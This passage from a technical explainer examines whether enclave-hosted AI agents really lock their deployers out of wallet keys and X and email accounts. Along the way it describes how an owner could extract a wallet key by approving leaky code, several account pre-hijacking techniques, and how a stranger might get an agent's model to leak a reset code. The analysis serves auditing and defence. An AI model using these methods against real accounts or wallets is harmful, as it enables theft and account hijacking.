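| Root key shared by threshold | *t* KMS nodes | One share, which is useless alone | The others carry on if at least *t* remain |

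A threshold of *t* nodes gives less protection if the nodes aren't independent, for example if one company operates all of them or they all use the same processor model with the same security hole. The threshold also protects only the root key. An application's derived key arrives whole in the application's enclave, so if the program leaks it, the number of KMS nodes doesn't matter.

Zhou and colleagues write that they rely on the KMS nodes' enclaves only to measure the software, not for the basic security of key management. This can be true only of the threshold version. If the nodes instead hold copies of the root key, a memory leak from one enclave exposes it, even if that enclave runs the correct software.

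The paper reports that both versions have been developed, but the evidence suggests that the one in use is copying. In the walkthrough, a KMS node stores both root keys as complete files on its encrypted disk, which doesn't fit a key split into shares. Phala's programming interface also lists several node "replicas" under one KMS contract, which is at least consistent with copying. EigenCloud's EigenCompute service gives each application a wallet derived from its app ID. In late 2025, EigenCloud reported that a single KMS node, run by EigenLabs on Google's cloud, served all applications and that a threshold version was still in development. Ada should therefore treat threshold protection as a plan unless the operator shows her that it is running.

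### Replacing a root key

Zhou and colleagues describe two ways a KMS can rotate its secrets if it suspects a leak. Under a threshold scheme, the nodes can replace their shares while keeping the same root key. In the example, they might switch from 7 + 4x to 7 + 9x, which changes node 2's share to 25. A thief who combined node 1's old share, 11, with node 2's new one would get a line that meets x = 0 at −3 instead of at the root key, 7. Application keys and wallet addresses stay the same, so the agent is unaffected.

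If the root key itself may have leaked, the KMS has to generate a new one. Both root keys remain valid for a handover period while applications re-encrypt their data under keys derived from the new one. The KMS then destroys the old root key.

Replacing the root key works better for disks than for wallets. A new root key gives the agent a new wallet key and a new address, and the agent has to move its funds there before the thief takes them. The old address stays on the blockchain, and any later payments to it may go to the thief. Even if the KMS destroys its copy of the old root key, the thief can still use the stolen copy to open any old disk images they have kept.

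Phala's *KMS and Key Delivery* also mentions rotating keys by changing the derivation inputs, after which "old keys are naturally phased out". The early draft included an epoch input for this. The walkthrough's formulas have no such input, so a program can only request a key at a new path, and any version of the program that requests the old path still gets the old key.

### How approving code gives access to the keys

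Zhou and colleagues describe two governance contracts, a shared KmsAuth and an AppAuth for each application. Some of the names have since changed. Phala's *Understanding Onchain KMS* keeps KmsAuth but calls the application's contract DstackApp, while *KMS and Key Delivery* calls the shared contract DstackKms.

DstackApp stores a list of allowed compose hashes, a list of allowed machines, and the address of an owner who can change both lists. When a CVM starts and requests keys, the KMS checks its quote against Intel's root certificates and then looks up the compose hash and the machine in the contract. If both are listed, it releases the application's keys.

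The contract records which code may have the keys but can't judge what the code does with them. An owner who wants the agent's wallet key can therefore get it legitimately, as far as every machine involved is concerned:

1. The agent runs version 1, which keeps its wallet key inside the enclave.
2. The owner prepares version 2, which requests the same path and prints the result.
3. The owner adds version 2's compose hash to the contract.
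4. Version 2 starts in a genuine enclave, and the KMS finds its hash on the list and releases the keys.
5. Version 2 prints the wallet key.

The honest agent can stay online during the theft, because Phala lets customers start a new instance under an existing app ID with a different configuration file. A quote that Ada obtains from version 1 then passes all seven of her checks.

With the contract in use, the theft leaves a trace. *Key Management Protocol For Decentralized Root-of-Trust* offers this as its answer to a deployer who installs leaky code and then removes it to hide the evidence. Every change to the authorisation of keys must start on the blockchain, where people can see it, and the draft claims that this gives the same security as existing smart contracts. That claim is too generous, because when the owner of an upgradable smart contract installs new code, anyone can examine the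 code on the blockchain. DstackApp receives only a 32-byte hash, which reveals nothing about the code until somebody publishes the configuration file and the images it names. Ada can see that the owner has approved something, but possibly not what it is. She should assume that any hash without published code belongs to a program that prints the keys.

Ada also has to check old approvals. *Multisig and Governance* explains that an update to a hash already on the list can skip the approval step. Phala's troubleshooting advice says that if an owner approves a hash and then abandons the update, the leftover entry is harmless because nobody uses it. But a leaky version that the owner approved last year could start tomorrow without any new transaction for Ada to notice.

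### Changing the code under an approved hash

If somebody points an image's tag at a different image, the KMS releases the keys to the new program, because the configuration file and its hash stay the same. Phala writes that a new image cannot run under an old hash, since changing the tag changes the configuration file, but this does not cover a new image under the same tag.

Phala's ERC-8004 guide seems to contain a second gap of this kind. The deployer supplies the address of a code repository and a version identifier as encrypted variables, and updates the agent by changing the identifier and redeploying. The compose hash covers the names of these variables but not their values. If the agent uses the values to fetch its code, as the guide implies, the deployer can, without asking the contract's owner, install a program that prints the wallet key. The guide is for a test network, but agents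 built from a template like this may well end up holding real money.

The same template offers a chat interface that runs Python code on request. Anyone relying on such an agent should check whether that code can reach the guest agent, because a visitor might then be able to request keys without an update.

### One owner, several signers, a delay, or no updates

On Phala Cloud in 2026, the deployer alone can approve new code by default under both available arrangements. With Phala's own centralised KMS, according to its March 2026 guide, the customer changes the configuration through a direct call to Phala, which leaves no public record on a blockchain. A customer who wants the contract must choose Ethereum or Base, another blockchain. The wallet that deploys the contract is its first owner and can approve new code with a single signature. On a self-hosted KMS, the list of approved code can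 be an ordinary configuration file, which whoever runs the server can edit.

By default, a dstack agent doesn't lock out its deployer. Even if the enclave is secure and the published code is trustworthy, the deployer can obtain the derived wallet key within minutes by approving another version of the code.

#### Several signers

The owner of DstackApp can transfer it to a Safe, a contract that acts only when enough of its signers agree, for example three out of five. Phala recommends requiring at least two thirds of the signatures. The deployer can then no longer approve code alone if the signers are different people. A Safe shows only the signers' addresses, so it does not reveal whether one person holds the keys to all of them.

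The signers also need some independence from the deployer. Lit Protocol, which runs its software on dstack, put its DstackApp contract under a Safe whose signers are Lit's own. This protects Lit's users against one rogue employee, but not against a decision by Lit as a company. For an agent run by a team of three, outsiders would have to hold enough signing keys to block an approval.

Signers can also approve bad code by mistake. Phala warns that the usual signing tool does not check whether a compose hash corresponds to anything meaningful, and tells signers to compare it with the source release themselves. This is harder because Phala's pages disagree about the hash function. *Understanding Onchain KMS* says SHA-256 and *Multisig and Governance* says Keccak-256, which give different results for the same file.

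#### A delay

The owner can also be a timelock, a contract that carries out an approved action only after a waiting period. Phala recommends 24 to 72 hours for new code. If Ada has money with the agent and can withdraw it at any time, a 48-hour delay protects her even against an owner acting alone, because she can take her money out before the new version receives any keys. But somebody has to watch the contract during the delay, and the deployer has to publish the new code when the delay begins so that others can examine it.

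A delay is less useful for a social-media account. Its followers have nothing to withdraw, but they can learn that someone else may soon control the account.

Phala describes the Safe and the timelock as optional additions that are not part of dstack. Phala's *Deploy On-chain KMS Smart Contracts* recommends using them together in production. If a deployer says only that the agent uses the "on-chain KMS", Ada can't tell whether either is in place.

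#### No updates

If the owner transfers the contract to an address that nobody controls, nobody can approve new code again. Phala warns that a mistyped address can cause this by accident, but a deployer who wants to be locked out might do it deliberately. This is the strongest of the four cases, though it has drawbacks that are easy to overlook.

If an agent has no owner, nobody can fix its bugs. It could also lose access to its wallet because of a firmware update. Phala explains that routine firmware maintenance can change a machine's identifier, and that an application can't start again on that machine until its owner adds the new identifier to the list of allowed machines. To avoid this, the deployer can switch on a setting that allows any machine within the KMS's scope before giving up ownership. This removes one restriction, but a machine's quote still has to pass the other checks.

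The deployer must also remove unwanted compose hashes from the list before transferring ownership. The list can't be changed after the transfer, and anyone able to start CVMs for the application can choose any version on it. Ada should ask for the code behind every remaining entry. She should also ask about removed entries, since a version that ran for ten minutes last year could have printed a wallet key that is still in use.

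DstackApp is a proxy, a contract that forwards calls to a second contract containing the rules. Anyone who can replace the second contract can change the rules, including the rule that determines who the owner is. Ada should also check that no one still has this right.

### The contract above the application's contract

Giving up DstackApp does not affect the shared contract. According to Lit Protocol, the KMS also checks at each start that the dstack operating-system image and the KMS's own measurement are each on a separate approved list. Both lists are in the shared contract, which belongs to a separate Safe under Phala's control.

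Phala writes that the start-up procedure has "no Phala-operated allowlist in the middle", which is true of the application's code. But Phala operates the shared contract, according to the same page, and the operating system handles an application's keys before the application does. If Phala's signers approved a doctored system image, it could copy an agent's keys even though the agent's compose hash had never changed, and a doctored KMS approved the same way could copy the root keys.

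There is no sign that Phala has done either, and such an approval would be visible on the blockchain. The lockout depends mainly on whether the deployer can influence those signers. A Phala Cloud customer probably can't. A deployer who runs a private dstack installation may also own the shared contract, in which case renouncing ownership of DstackApp achieves very little. Ada should look up the owners of both contracts.

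### Having a network sign instead

Any KMS that delivers keys puts the whole private key in the agent's enclave at some point, and a program there can print it. Threshold signing avoids this because the nodes of a network hold shares of the wallet key and produce signatures together, without anyone assembling the key.

Schnorr signatures, on which Solana's signature scheme is based, show how this is possible. Leaving out details, the signer computes

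s = r + c·k

where *k* is the private key, *r* a random number used only once, and *c* a hash that depends on the message. Suppose that the nodes have Shamir shares *k*ᵢ and *r*ᵢ of the two secrets. Each node computes *s*ᵢ = *r*ᵢ + *c*·*k*ᵢ and publishes the result. Because the formula only adds and multiplies by a known number, the *s*ᵢ are shares of *s*, and anyone can combine enough of them into the finished signature. The nodes never reveal their shares of *k*.

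The blockchain project NEAR uses threshold signing in its Shade Agents. Each agent's program runs in an enclave, and a contract on NEAR's blockchain checks the program's attestation against a list of approved code. If the code is on the list, the contract lets the program request signatures from a network of nodes that jointly hold the key.

An attacker who breaks into the enclave of an agent that uses dstack's KMS can copy the agent's key and keep it permanently. If the agent relies on a signing network instead, the attacker can request signatures only until the contract stops accepting that enclave. The contract can also impose limits, such as a maximum amount per day, that hold even if the agent's own code is malicious.

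Someone still has to maintain the list of approved code. A deployer who controls it can take the agent's entire balance without ever seeing the key, by approving a version that requests a signature for the transfer. Ada would have to examine the contract's owner, signers and delays, as she would with DstackApp. She would also have to trust that fewer than *t* nodes would ever sign without the agent's request.

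Threshold signing doesn't work for an agent's other accounts. Email providers and social networks require a complete password, so the enclave has to hold the whole password to log in.

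## How does an enclave take over an existing email and social-media account?

A password that only the enclave knows does not secure an account if somebody else can reset it. A wallet's signature can be verified mathematically, but an account on X is an entry in the company's database, and the company gives access to anyone who meets its rules. The deployer knew the original password and has usually also registered their own email address or phone number, which they may be able to use to reset the new one.

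X's *About account security* warns users against giving their password to third parties, who then "have complete control of your account and can lock you out". A deployer who wants to be locked out gives the password to a program in an enclave, which acts as the third party.

### The tee_hee_he procedure

Nous Research built the agent tee_hee_he with Teleport, a project of the Ethereum research organisation Flashbots. To give the agent sole access to its X account, Nous Research required that the password be generated inside the enclave and stay there. The account must have no phone number, no connected apps and no open sessions from before the takeover, and only the agent may be able to open the linked mailbox.

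1. The deployer gives the program the address and password of an account at Cock.li, an email provider. The program opens the account in a browser inside the enclave, checks that it has no recovery options, and replaces the password with one it has just generated.
2. The program logs in to X with the deployer's password and replaces that password too.
3. It changes the email address linked to the X account to the Cock.li address.
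4. It removes any phone number, connected apps and existing sessions.
5. It requests an OAuth token that allows reading, posting and direct messages, and logs in to X as the agent to approve the request.

After that, the program uses the token because it offers a simpler interface than a web browser. tee_hee_he posted every 30 minutes.

The team chose Cock.li because a user can open an account there without a recovery address, so a lost password can't be recovered. But this is only the provider's policy, and its administrators can presumably still change a password in their own database. The procedure also depends on the provider's website. A user in the Privacy Guides forum thread *Cock.li being taken down by the government?* reported that the mail servers worked but that password changes were temporarily impossible. In that situation, a program would have to stop at the first step.

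Nous Research's alternative was to run a mail server inside the enclave. This removes the email provider but requires a domain name, because other mail servers use the domain's records to find where to deliver the agent's mail. If the deployer owns the domain, they can redirect the mail to their own machine and collect a password-reset code.

### Why the email account comes first

Anyone who can read the linked mailbox can choose a new X password. According to X's *How to reset a lost or forgotten password*, resetting a password requires access to the linked email address or phone number, where X sends a code valid for 60 minutes. X's *Help with email address access* tells users who have lost access to the mailbox to regain it through their email provider before requesting a new X password.

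Suppose that a program takes over the accounts in the wrong order, starting with X:

1. At 12:00 the program changes the X password, and the deployer's old password stops working.
2. At 12:01 the deployer asks X for a reset code and reads it in the mailbox, which they still control.
3. The deployer enters the code and chooses another password. The program's password stops working, and the program can't request a code of its own because it has no mailbox.

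The deployer can also wait a week, until the program has announced that it controls the account, and then do the same thing.

A deployer can still interfere when the program takes over the accounts in the correct order, for example by changing the X password while the program is working on the mailbox. But then the program can't log in to X, so it doesn't announce a takeover.

Starting with the mailbox is also practical, because the program must be able to open it before it can switch the X account to that address. An older copy of X's *How to update your email* says the user must enter the account's password and then confirm the change through an email to the new address.

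The table follows the published sequence for an X account that is initially linked to the deployer's personal mailbox and phone number. The deployer is logged in on a phone and has connected a scheduling service that can post. The table leaves out X and Cock.li, whose staff could give someone access at any point.

| Latest step | How the deployer can still act as the agent | How the deployer can still regain the account | What the enclave controls |
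|---|---|---|---|
| None | X password, phone session, scheduling service | Personal mailbox, phone number | Nothing |
| New Cock.li password | Unchanged | Unchanged | The new mailbox |
| New X password | Scheduling service; phone session if X fails to end it | Personal mailbox, phone number | The new mailbox and the X password |
| X linked to the Cock.li address | Unchanged | Phone number; a reset code already received | The same, plus resets by email |
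| Phone number removed | Unchanged | A reset code already received | Unchanged |
| Apps and sessions removed | None of the original ways | A reset code already received, until it expires | Unchanged |
| Token obtained | None of the original ways, though the owner of the developer app may have some influence | A reset code already received, until it expires | The same, plus the token |

Ending the sessions is a safeguard because a password change can fail to log out other devices. X normally logs a user out everywhere else when they change their password, but SoyaCincau's *Changed your Twitter password recently* (2022) reported a bug that had left phones logged in after a reset.

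The deployer might be able to retake the X account with a reset code, because the program changes the password while the deployer's mailbox and phone number are still linked to the account. The deployer can request a code a few seconds before the program removes the phone number, and enter it half an hour later. X's instructions don't mention whether removing a number cancels codes already sent to it. To be safe, the program could wait more than an hour after removing the last of the deployer's contact details, then change the password and check all the settings again before announcing anything.

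When an account's linked address changes, X emails the previous address so that a hijacking victim can try to regain the account. X also keeps old addresses on file for security purposes, according to its *How to update your email address*. The takeover must look much like a hijacking to X, because someone logs in from an unfamiliar machine and replaces the password and all the contact details within minutes. A deployer could report it as a hijacking and describe the events truthfully. Opening the X account with the Cock.li address from the start avoids the alert and leaves X with no older address on file.

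### Marlin's Oyster agent

Marlin runs a marketplace called Oyster where customers rent enclaves. *Oyster twitter agent*, an undated design note, describes a takeover in which the deployer first opens an X account using an email address that expires after ten minutes. The deployer then completes the application for X's developer portal, where developers register apps and manage their tokens. Next, the program in the enclave resets the X password, logs in to the portal with the new password and regenerates all the tokens. It publishes posts through Tweepy, a programming library for X.

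Regenerating the tokens matters because the deployer used the portal first and could have copied the originals. The design also puts the developer app under the same X account that the enclave takes over. The tee_hee_he README, Nous Research and Teleport's *Setting Your Pet Rock Free* (2024), lists a developer account as a requirement, but its steps don't include taking over that account.

The program that operates the browser in Marlin's design is itself an AI agent, built with a tool called browser-use. A language model chooses what to click and type on each page. This may cope better with a redesigned page than a fixed script would, but outsiders have more to check. Ada should find out whether the new password ever appears in the text or screenshots that the program sends to the model. If it does, the model's provider receives it, and the deployer may be able to read it in the logs of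 the API account they pay for.

Marlin later turned the idea into a documented product. Its *Twitter Agent Service* calls the account "encumbered" and offers the account's keys and tokens to other applications in the same enclave so they can post through it. According to *Integrate Twitter Agent Service into Your Enclave Application*, the deployer supplies the current passwords for the X and email accounts, along with an OpenAI key. This version therefore seems designed for a long-lived email account.

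The local test in Marlin's *Step 2* ends with the developer fetching the new keys and tokens through a web request. If the deployed service also answered this request when it came from outside the enclave, the deployer could collect the tokens and post as the agent. Ada should check which addresses the service accepts the request from.

### A mailbox that expires

With an expiring mailbox, the enclave doesn't need to take over an email account. Once the address expires, the deployer can't use it to request a reset code, and there is no email password to remember.

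But the deployer controls the mailbox for the first ten minutes and can request a code just before the mailbox expires. X's codes are valid for 60 minutes, so this one could work for almost an hour afterward. As with tee_hee_he, the program would need to change the password again later.

If the program uses the "forgot password" procedure, it needs a code from the mailbox, so the deployer must finish opening the account and registering as a developer early enough for the code to arrive before the ten-minute mailbox expires. Marlin says its later service takes 15 to 20 minutes to run, which would be too long if the program needed an email near the end. A program that logs in with the deployer's password and changes it from the settings page doesn't have this problem, because X asks only for the current password.

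The disposable-mail service promises that the address will expire, but its operator still controls the domain and could receive mail for any address there. If the service ever gave the same address to another visitor, that person could request a reset code and take over the agent's account.

The agent can't receive mail either once its mailbox expires. X says that if it suspects a hijacking, it may reset the account's password and email a link for choosing a new one. An agent with an expired mailbox and no phone number would never receive that link, and could no longer use the account the enclave had taken over. A lasting mailbox that only the enclave can open seems clearly better for an agent that is supposed to run for months.

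If an agent keeps a mailbox long-term, a separate program should handle it, as with a wallet key, so that the agent's language model can't read the mail. Otherwise, a stranger could trigger a password-reset email and might then get the model to repeat the code in a reply. Malwarebytes' *X Money rollout linked to password-reset attacks* (2026) reports that X users began receiving unrequested reset emails and codes on 1 September, though X had found no evidence of successful takeovers.

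### Random or derived passwords

An enclave can generate a password from random numbers or derive it from a key it gets from a KMS. tee_hee_he generated its passwords inside the enclave, while the Oyster design derives the passwords for both accounts from a key. Either kind of password can be long enough that nobody will guess it. The two kinds differ in what happens after a crash and in who might obtain the password later.

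A random password exists only where the program has stored it. *Help, I've Been Locked Out of Twitter* (2018), a first-person account from the Boston broadcaster WGBH, describes a man who reset his Twitter password with a password manager and believed he had saved the new one, but hadn't. The old password no longer worked, and he had never given Twitter a phone number. A program that crashes between changing the password and saving it is also left without a working password. If it has lost access to the mailbox as well, the account is orphaned, meaning it still exists but neither the agent nor the deployer can log in.

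Random secrets are particularly awkward on Oyster. Marlin's *Persistent keys* explains that a secret generated inside one of its enclaves doesn't survive a restart, and Marlin's example for the X service rents the enclave for just 60 minutes. A program that can derive the password simply computes it again. In outline:

K = HKDF(R, identity)

pₙ = Encode(HKDF(K, "x-password" ‖ n))

Here *R* is the root secret of the KMS, *K* is the application's key, and *Encode* turns the result into characters that X accepts. The counter *n* lets the program change its password. Without it, the program would always derive the same password, even after a leak. The counter needn't be secret, so the program can store it anywhere.

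The choice of *identity* determines who can recompute the password. Marlin's *Nautilus KMS* offers two kinds and recommends the image variant by default. In this variant, the key depends on the enclave's measurements and startup data, which Marlin combines into an image ID. New code gets a different key, as it does under the formula in *Key Management Protocol For Decentralized Root-of-Trust*. A leaky new version therefore can't derive the password, but a harmless update also cuts the agent off from its account. Even an unused startup parameter changes the image ID. For the agent to keep access after an update, the old version would have to pass the password to the new one, and Ada would have to check which programs the old version would pass it to.

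The contract variant derives *K* from the address of a blockchain contract instead. Marlin's *Contract-based access control* shows that two images with different IDs get the same key once the contract approves both. The standard contract in that guide lets its deployer approve images. For an X account, the deployer could then approve a program that derives *p*ₙ and prints it, without needing a copy of the agent's disk. The owner of a dstack contract can likewise approve a program that prints a wallet key. Marlin warns that this variant is only as secure as the contract's approval process.

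| Password | After a crash | After a code update | What the deployer could use to learn it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random, in memory only | Lost | Lost | A leak in the running program |
| Random, saved to dstack's encrypted disk | Kept, if the program saved it in time and the disk survives | Kept, if the same instance continues | A leak, or approval of a leaky version that runs with the original disk |
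| Derived, image variant | Recomputed | Lost, unless the old version hands it over | A leak in that same program |
| Derived, contract variant | Recomputed | Recomputed | A leak, or approval of any leaky version |

The image variant looks like the best of these for a deployer who wants to be locked out and can do without updates. Marlin's X service probably uses it, because its test settings fetch keys through port 1100, which Marlin assigns to the image variant. But the example configuration identifies the service's container only by the tag "latest". If the image ID covers only the text of that configuration, whoever controls the container's registry account could substitute a different program that derives the same passwords.

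Derived passwords also depend on the KMS keeping *R* both secret and available. If the KMS loses *R*, the agents can't recompute their passwords after a restart. A May 2026 Marlin forum post discusses an additional backup path for this root secret. A backup makes losing *R* less likely but adds a place where someone could steal it.

### When the procedure stops halfway

Marlin warns developers of "a significant risk of losing access to your Twitter and email accounts" when they start the service. The warning is in the instructions for the local test, which requires the passwords of real accounts, so a developer would be wise to use accounts they don't mind losing.

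The effect of an interruption depends on when it happens. If the program stops after changing the mailbox password but before changing the X password, the deployer may lose the mailbox but can still log in to X and link the account to a different one.

The most delicate step is submitting a new X password. If the connection drops before X replies, the program can't tell whether X accepted the change, so it needs both the old and new passwords to try each one. If the new password is random, the program should save it to disk before submitting it. With derived passwords, the program can try *p*ₙ and *p*ₙ₊₁ without having saved either. If neither works, it can ask for a reset code, but only if it still controls the linked mailbox. It should therefore check that it can log out of the mailbox and back in with the new email password before it changes anything on X.

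If the program crashes and loses the X password while the deployer's phone number is still linked, the deployer can recover the account, but the lockout has failed. If a crash destroys the email and X passwords after the program has removed the number, nobody can log in. According to X, a user with access to neither the linked phone nor the linked email can't recover the password and may have to open a new account. The old posts would stay online, and neither the agent nor the deployer could delete them. It is therefore safer for the program to remove the number only after it has logged in again with the new X password and received a test email in the linked mailbox.

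A half-finished takeover can also look complete. If the program crashes before disconnecting the scheduling service, it may restart, log in and begin posting while the deployer can still post through the service. To prevent this, the program can record each completed step and recheck every setting whenever it starts. It should request the quote naming the account only after all the checks succeed. Nous Research writes that its program requested this quote immediately after resetting the password. If this is literally true, the program had not yet removed the phone number and the connected apps.

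Nous Research intended to limit the lockout by having tee_hee_he release its credentials after seven days, which would also let the team transfer the account to another AI agent. This departed from the README's requirement that the transfer be irreversible. It also would not have recovered the account if the machine had failed before the seventh day, because the program running on it had to print the credentials.

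## Which ways into an account can survive a password change?

After changing the X password, tee_hee_he's program deleted any linked phone number, connected apps and open sessions. Nous Research drew up that list for one account in 2024, and it leaves out other ways in, such as a passkey or a second user with permission to post. A deployer may have held an account for months before the enclave takes it over, and may have set up some ways back in on purpose and forgotten about others. An outsider can't tell which, so they have to worry about both.

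Sudhodanan and Paverd (2022), in *Pre-hijacked accounts*, describe an account by the values that a service uses to recognise its user. In simplified form:

S = (email address, phone number, password, linked identities, open sessions)

A password change replaces one of these values. The service may also clear some of the others, but any it doesn't clear still work for whoever set them up.

### Accounts prepared for somebody else

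Sudhodanan and Paverd studied *pre-hijacking*, in which an attacker opens an account with the email address of somebody who hasn't joined the service yet. When the victim later tries to sign up, they learn that the account exists, reset the password and start using it. Before the reset, the attacker has already arranged a way back in. A deployer who prepares an account for a program in an enclave can do the same to the program.

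The simplest method is to stay logged in. In the *unexpired session attack*, the attacker keeps a session active, if necessary with a script that periodically performs some action. If the service doesn't end old sessions when the password changes, a deployer can keep access with just a phone that is still logged in.

In the *Trojan identifier attack*, the attacker adds their own login to the account, such as a Google account, a second email address or a phone number. Some services send one-time login links to an added address or number. A deployer can use such a link to log in without changing the password, so the program's password keeps working and the program may not detect the login.

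The *unexpired email change attack* takes more planning. Suppose that the agent's account is already linked to the mailbox that the enclave will control:

1. On Monday the deployer asks the service to move the account to a different address, which they own. The service sends a confirmation link there, and the deployer leaves it unopened.
2. On Tuesday the program changes the password. The settings page shows the right address, so the program announces that it controls the account.
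3. On Wednesday the deployer opens the link. The service changes the address, and the deployer resets the password by email.

The link has to remain valid until Wednesday, and the password change must not have cancelled it. Some services also require whoever opens the link to be logged in. The attacker must then get the victim to open it, which may be easy if the victim is an AI agent that follows links from strangers in a browser logged in to its own account. This variant fails if the service requires a code as well as a click.

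The other two attacks involve an identity provider, a company such as Google or Apple whose accounts people can use to log in elsewhere. In the *classic-federated merge attack*, the attacker opens an account with a password, the victim later signs up through "Sign in with Google", and the service merges the two accounts but leaves the attacker's password working. A deployer could keep access this way if the program took over the account by linking a Google identity and never replaced the password.

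In the *non-verifying identity provider attack*, the attacker registers the victim's address with a provider that doesn't check who owns it, then logs in through that provider. This probably matters little for a personal account on X. But some business services let customers connect their own identity provider, and a deployer who runs that provider could use it to log in as the agent.

Between January and June 2021, Sudhodanan and Paverd tested 75 of the 150 most popular websites by hand, using accounts they opened for the purpose. At least 35 were vulnerable to one or more attacks. The unexpired session attack succeeded on 19 of the 74 services where they could try it, the merge attack on 13 of 54, the Trojan identifier attack on 12 of 49 and the unexpired email change attack on 11 of 72. They could test the non-verifying provider attack on only three services, and it succeeded on one, Zoom.

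Some of these services have since changed. LinkedIn used to leave other sessions open unless the user ticked a box, but now ends them by default. Zoom fixed both of its vulnerabilities. But Instagram replied that users are responsible for spotting unfamiliar phone numbers and addresses in their profiles, and WordPress.com marked the report of sessions that stayed open after a password reset as "Not Applicable". The 2021 counts are therefore a poor guide to any particular service today, but the five methods are still worth checking for.

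The paper's main remedy is for services to confirm that a new user owns an email address before letting them use the account. That doesn't stop a deployer, who, unlike the paper's attacker, did own the address. But the paper assumes a victim who ignores warning emails and doesn't look through the settings, whereas a program can check the settings every time. The paper recommends that after a password reset, a service should end all other sessions, cancel pending changes of address, and ask the user which linked identities, addresses and phone numbers to keep. A takeover program can do much of this itself if the service doesn't.

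### Sessions that stay open

Krause, Suray and colleagues (2025) examined 111 popular websites in *An Analysis of the Security, Usability, and Automation Capabilities*, using accounts opened between September 2024 and February 2025. Logged-in users could change their password on 96 of them. Eight of the 96 told users that the change would end all sessions, and 12 that it would end all sessions except the current one. The researchers recorded these notices but didn't test whether old sessions still worked, so some of the other sites may end sessions without saying so.

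Besides posting, a deployer with an old session might be able to change the password and lock the program out. On 16 of the 96 websites, the password-change form had no field for the current password, so an open session would be enough to set a new one unless the website checks the user's identity in some other way.

Changing an X account's password is supposed to end all other sessions, but a bug once left phones logged in, so a program shouldn't rely on the password change alone. Security Alliance, which publishes security guides, points to a button in X's settings that logs out all other sessions. The program can also press that button, then read the list of sessions to confirm that only its own remains.

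According to Google, a new password signs the user out everywhere except on devices they use to verify their identity, some devices with third-party apps that have access to the account, and certain home devices. Suppose the agent's mailbox is a Gmail account that the deployer opened on their own phone, and Google has been using that phone to confirm logins. The phone may stay signed in after the enclave changes the password. The deployer could then ask X for a reset code and read it on the phone.

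Before changing the password, the program can find out which devices will stay signed in. iDownloadBlog (2024) reported that Google lists these devices before the user confirms the new password and lets the user remove devices afterwards. The program should remove all of them, including any the deployer describes as harmless.

### Passkeys and second factors

A passkey is a pair of keys that can replace a password. The service stores the public key, and the user's device proves at each login that it has the private one. This process doesn't use the password, so a program should assume that old passkeys still work after a password change. Google's *Sign in with a passkey instead of a password* says users can find existing passkeys among the account's sign-in options, so the program can look there for any it didn't create.

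The deployer may have several copies of a passkey. Google's *Use passwords & passkeys across your devices* says a passkey saved in Google's password manager works on every device signed in to the same Google account. If the deployer created a passkey for the agent's X account, it may be on a phone, a tablet and two laptops. Deleting it from one device, even on video, would not prove that the other copies are gone. The program has to remove the public key from X, which makes all the copies useless.

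Many accounts also ask for a second factor, such as a six-digit code from an authenticator app. The app computes the code from a secret seed and the time *t* in seconds, usually in steps of 30:

code = F(seed, ⌊t / 30⌋)

The service displays the authenticator app's seed once, normally as a QR code, and anyone with a photograph of it can compute the app's login codes indefinitely. The deployer may also have a paper copy of the backup codes, which the service issues in case the user loses the app. Changing the password normally invalidates neither the seed nor the backup codes. Neither is enough to log in, but a deployer who also obtains a password-reset code can use either one to complete the login.

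The program should therefore turn off the old authenticator, set up a new one and generate new backup codes. According to iDownloadBlog, Google may ask for confirmation on a phone, an authenticator code or a backup code before it accepts a new password, so the deployer has to be ready to supply one of these or switch off the second factor beforehand.

Sudhodanan and Paverd recommend activating a second factor because, if the service implements it correctly, it stops an attacker from logging in to an account they prepared in advance. They add that the service must also end any sessions that began before the second factor was activated. If only the enclave knows the seed for an agent's second factor, a deployer who can read the agent's mail could reset the password but would still lack the code, provided the service asks for it after a reset. The seed is also one more secret that the program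 could lose in a crash.

### One login for several services

An agent may use one Google account to log in to several other services. *O Single Sign-Off, Where Art Thou?* (Ghasemisharif, Ramesh and colleagues, 2018) examines what happens when an attacker takes over the account at the identity provider (here, Google). According to the security company Duo, the researchers found that 6.3 per cent of the million most popular websites supported this kind of login, and that attackers could use stolen tokens to enter accounts on other services without the password. Each website also keeps its own session after the login, and that session can continue when the Google password changes.

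The researchers called for a "single sign-off", which Help Net Security's *The single sign-on account hijacking threat* described as one action by the user that would set off a chain of revocations across all the associated accounts. Google's cross-account protection now partly does this by sending security alerts to connected services so that they can log the user out. But according to Notebookcheck's *Your new Google password does not lock out the old apps* (September 2026), services have to opt in, and an ordinary password change doesn't trigger an alert. Eight years after the paper, a program that takes over a Google account still has to visit every service the account can open and end the deployer's sessions there.

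If the deployer linked their personal Google account to one of the agent's accounts, they can still log in with it after the agent's password changes. The program has to unlink the Google account in the settings of the agent's account, because changing the password of the agent's own mailbox doesn't remove the link.

### Delegates and other people with permission

X lets the owner of an account give other accounts permission to act for it. These delegates log in with their own passwords, so changing the password of the agent's account probably doesn't affect their access. ChainPatrol's *How to Recover a Compromised X Account (2025)* advises victims to check the delegation settings and revoke unfamiliar accounts as a separate step. ChainPatrol sells security services, and its advice is weak evidence of how X works. But X's *Help with my compromised account* doesn't mention delegates, passkeys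 or pending changes of address. A program whose developers relied on X's instructions could miss all three.

X's instructions list changing the password and removing connected apps as separate steps. There are further questions about the tokens those apps use.

### The mailbox

Besides open sessions, passkeys and second factors, the mailbox that receives X's reset codes has some access routes that a social-media account doesn't. The easiest to overlook is automatic forwarding. If the deployer sets a rule that copies every message to their personal address, the rule keeps working after the mailbox password changes, because forwarding doesn't require a login. The deployer can then request a reset code from X and receive a copy. If a filter also deletes messages from X as they arrive, the program never sees the code.

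App passwords are extra passwords that a provider issues for mail programs that can't handle a second factor. Android Central's *How to completely reset your Google login across every device* lists revoking them by hand as a separate step. A takeover program should do this too, even if the provider promises to cancel them, and should check whether any other user has permission to read the mailbox. Permissions previously granted to apps can also survive a password change. Notebookcheck, citing Google's documentation, reports that the change ends an app's access if it includes Gmail, but not if it covers only photos, contacts or files.

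X has a setting called password reset protection, which requires anyone requesting a reset to enter the account's email address or phone number first. This helps against strangers but not against the deployer, who already knows the address. It also doesn't help if the deployer can still use an old address. McAfee's *X (Twitter) Account Hacked* tells hijacking victims to check the alert X sends to the previous email address for an option to undo the change. X's description of the alert doesn't mention such an option. If it exists, the deployer may be able to reverse the enclave's change of address, so this should be tested on a spare account before anyone relies on the procedure.

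The deployer can also ask X's support staff to return the account, though X sends its instructions to the email address associated with it.

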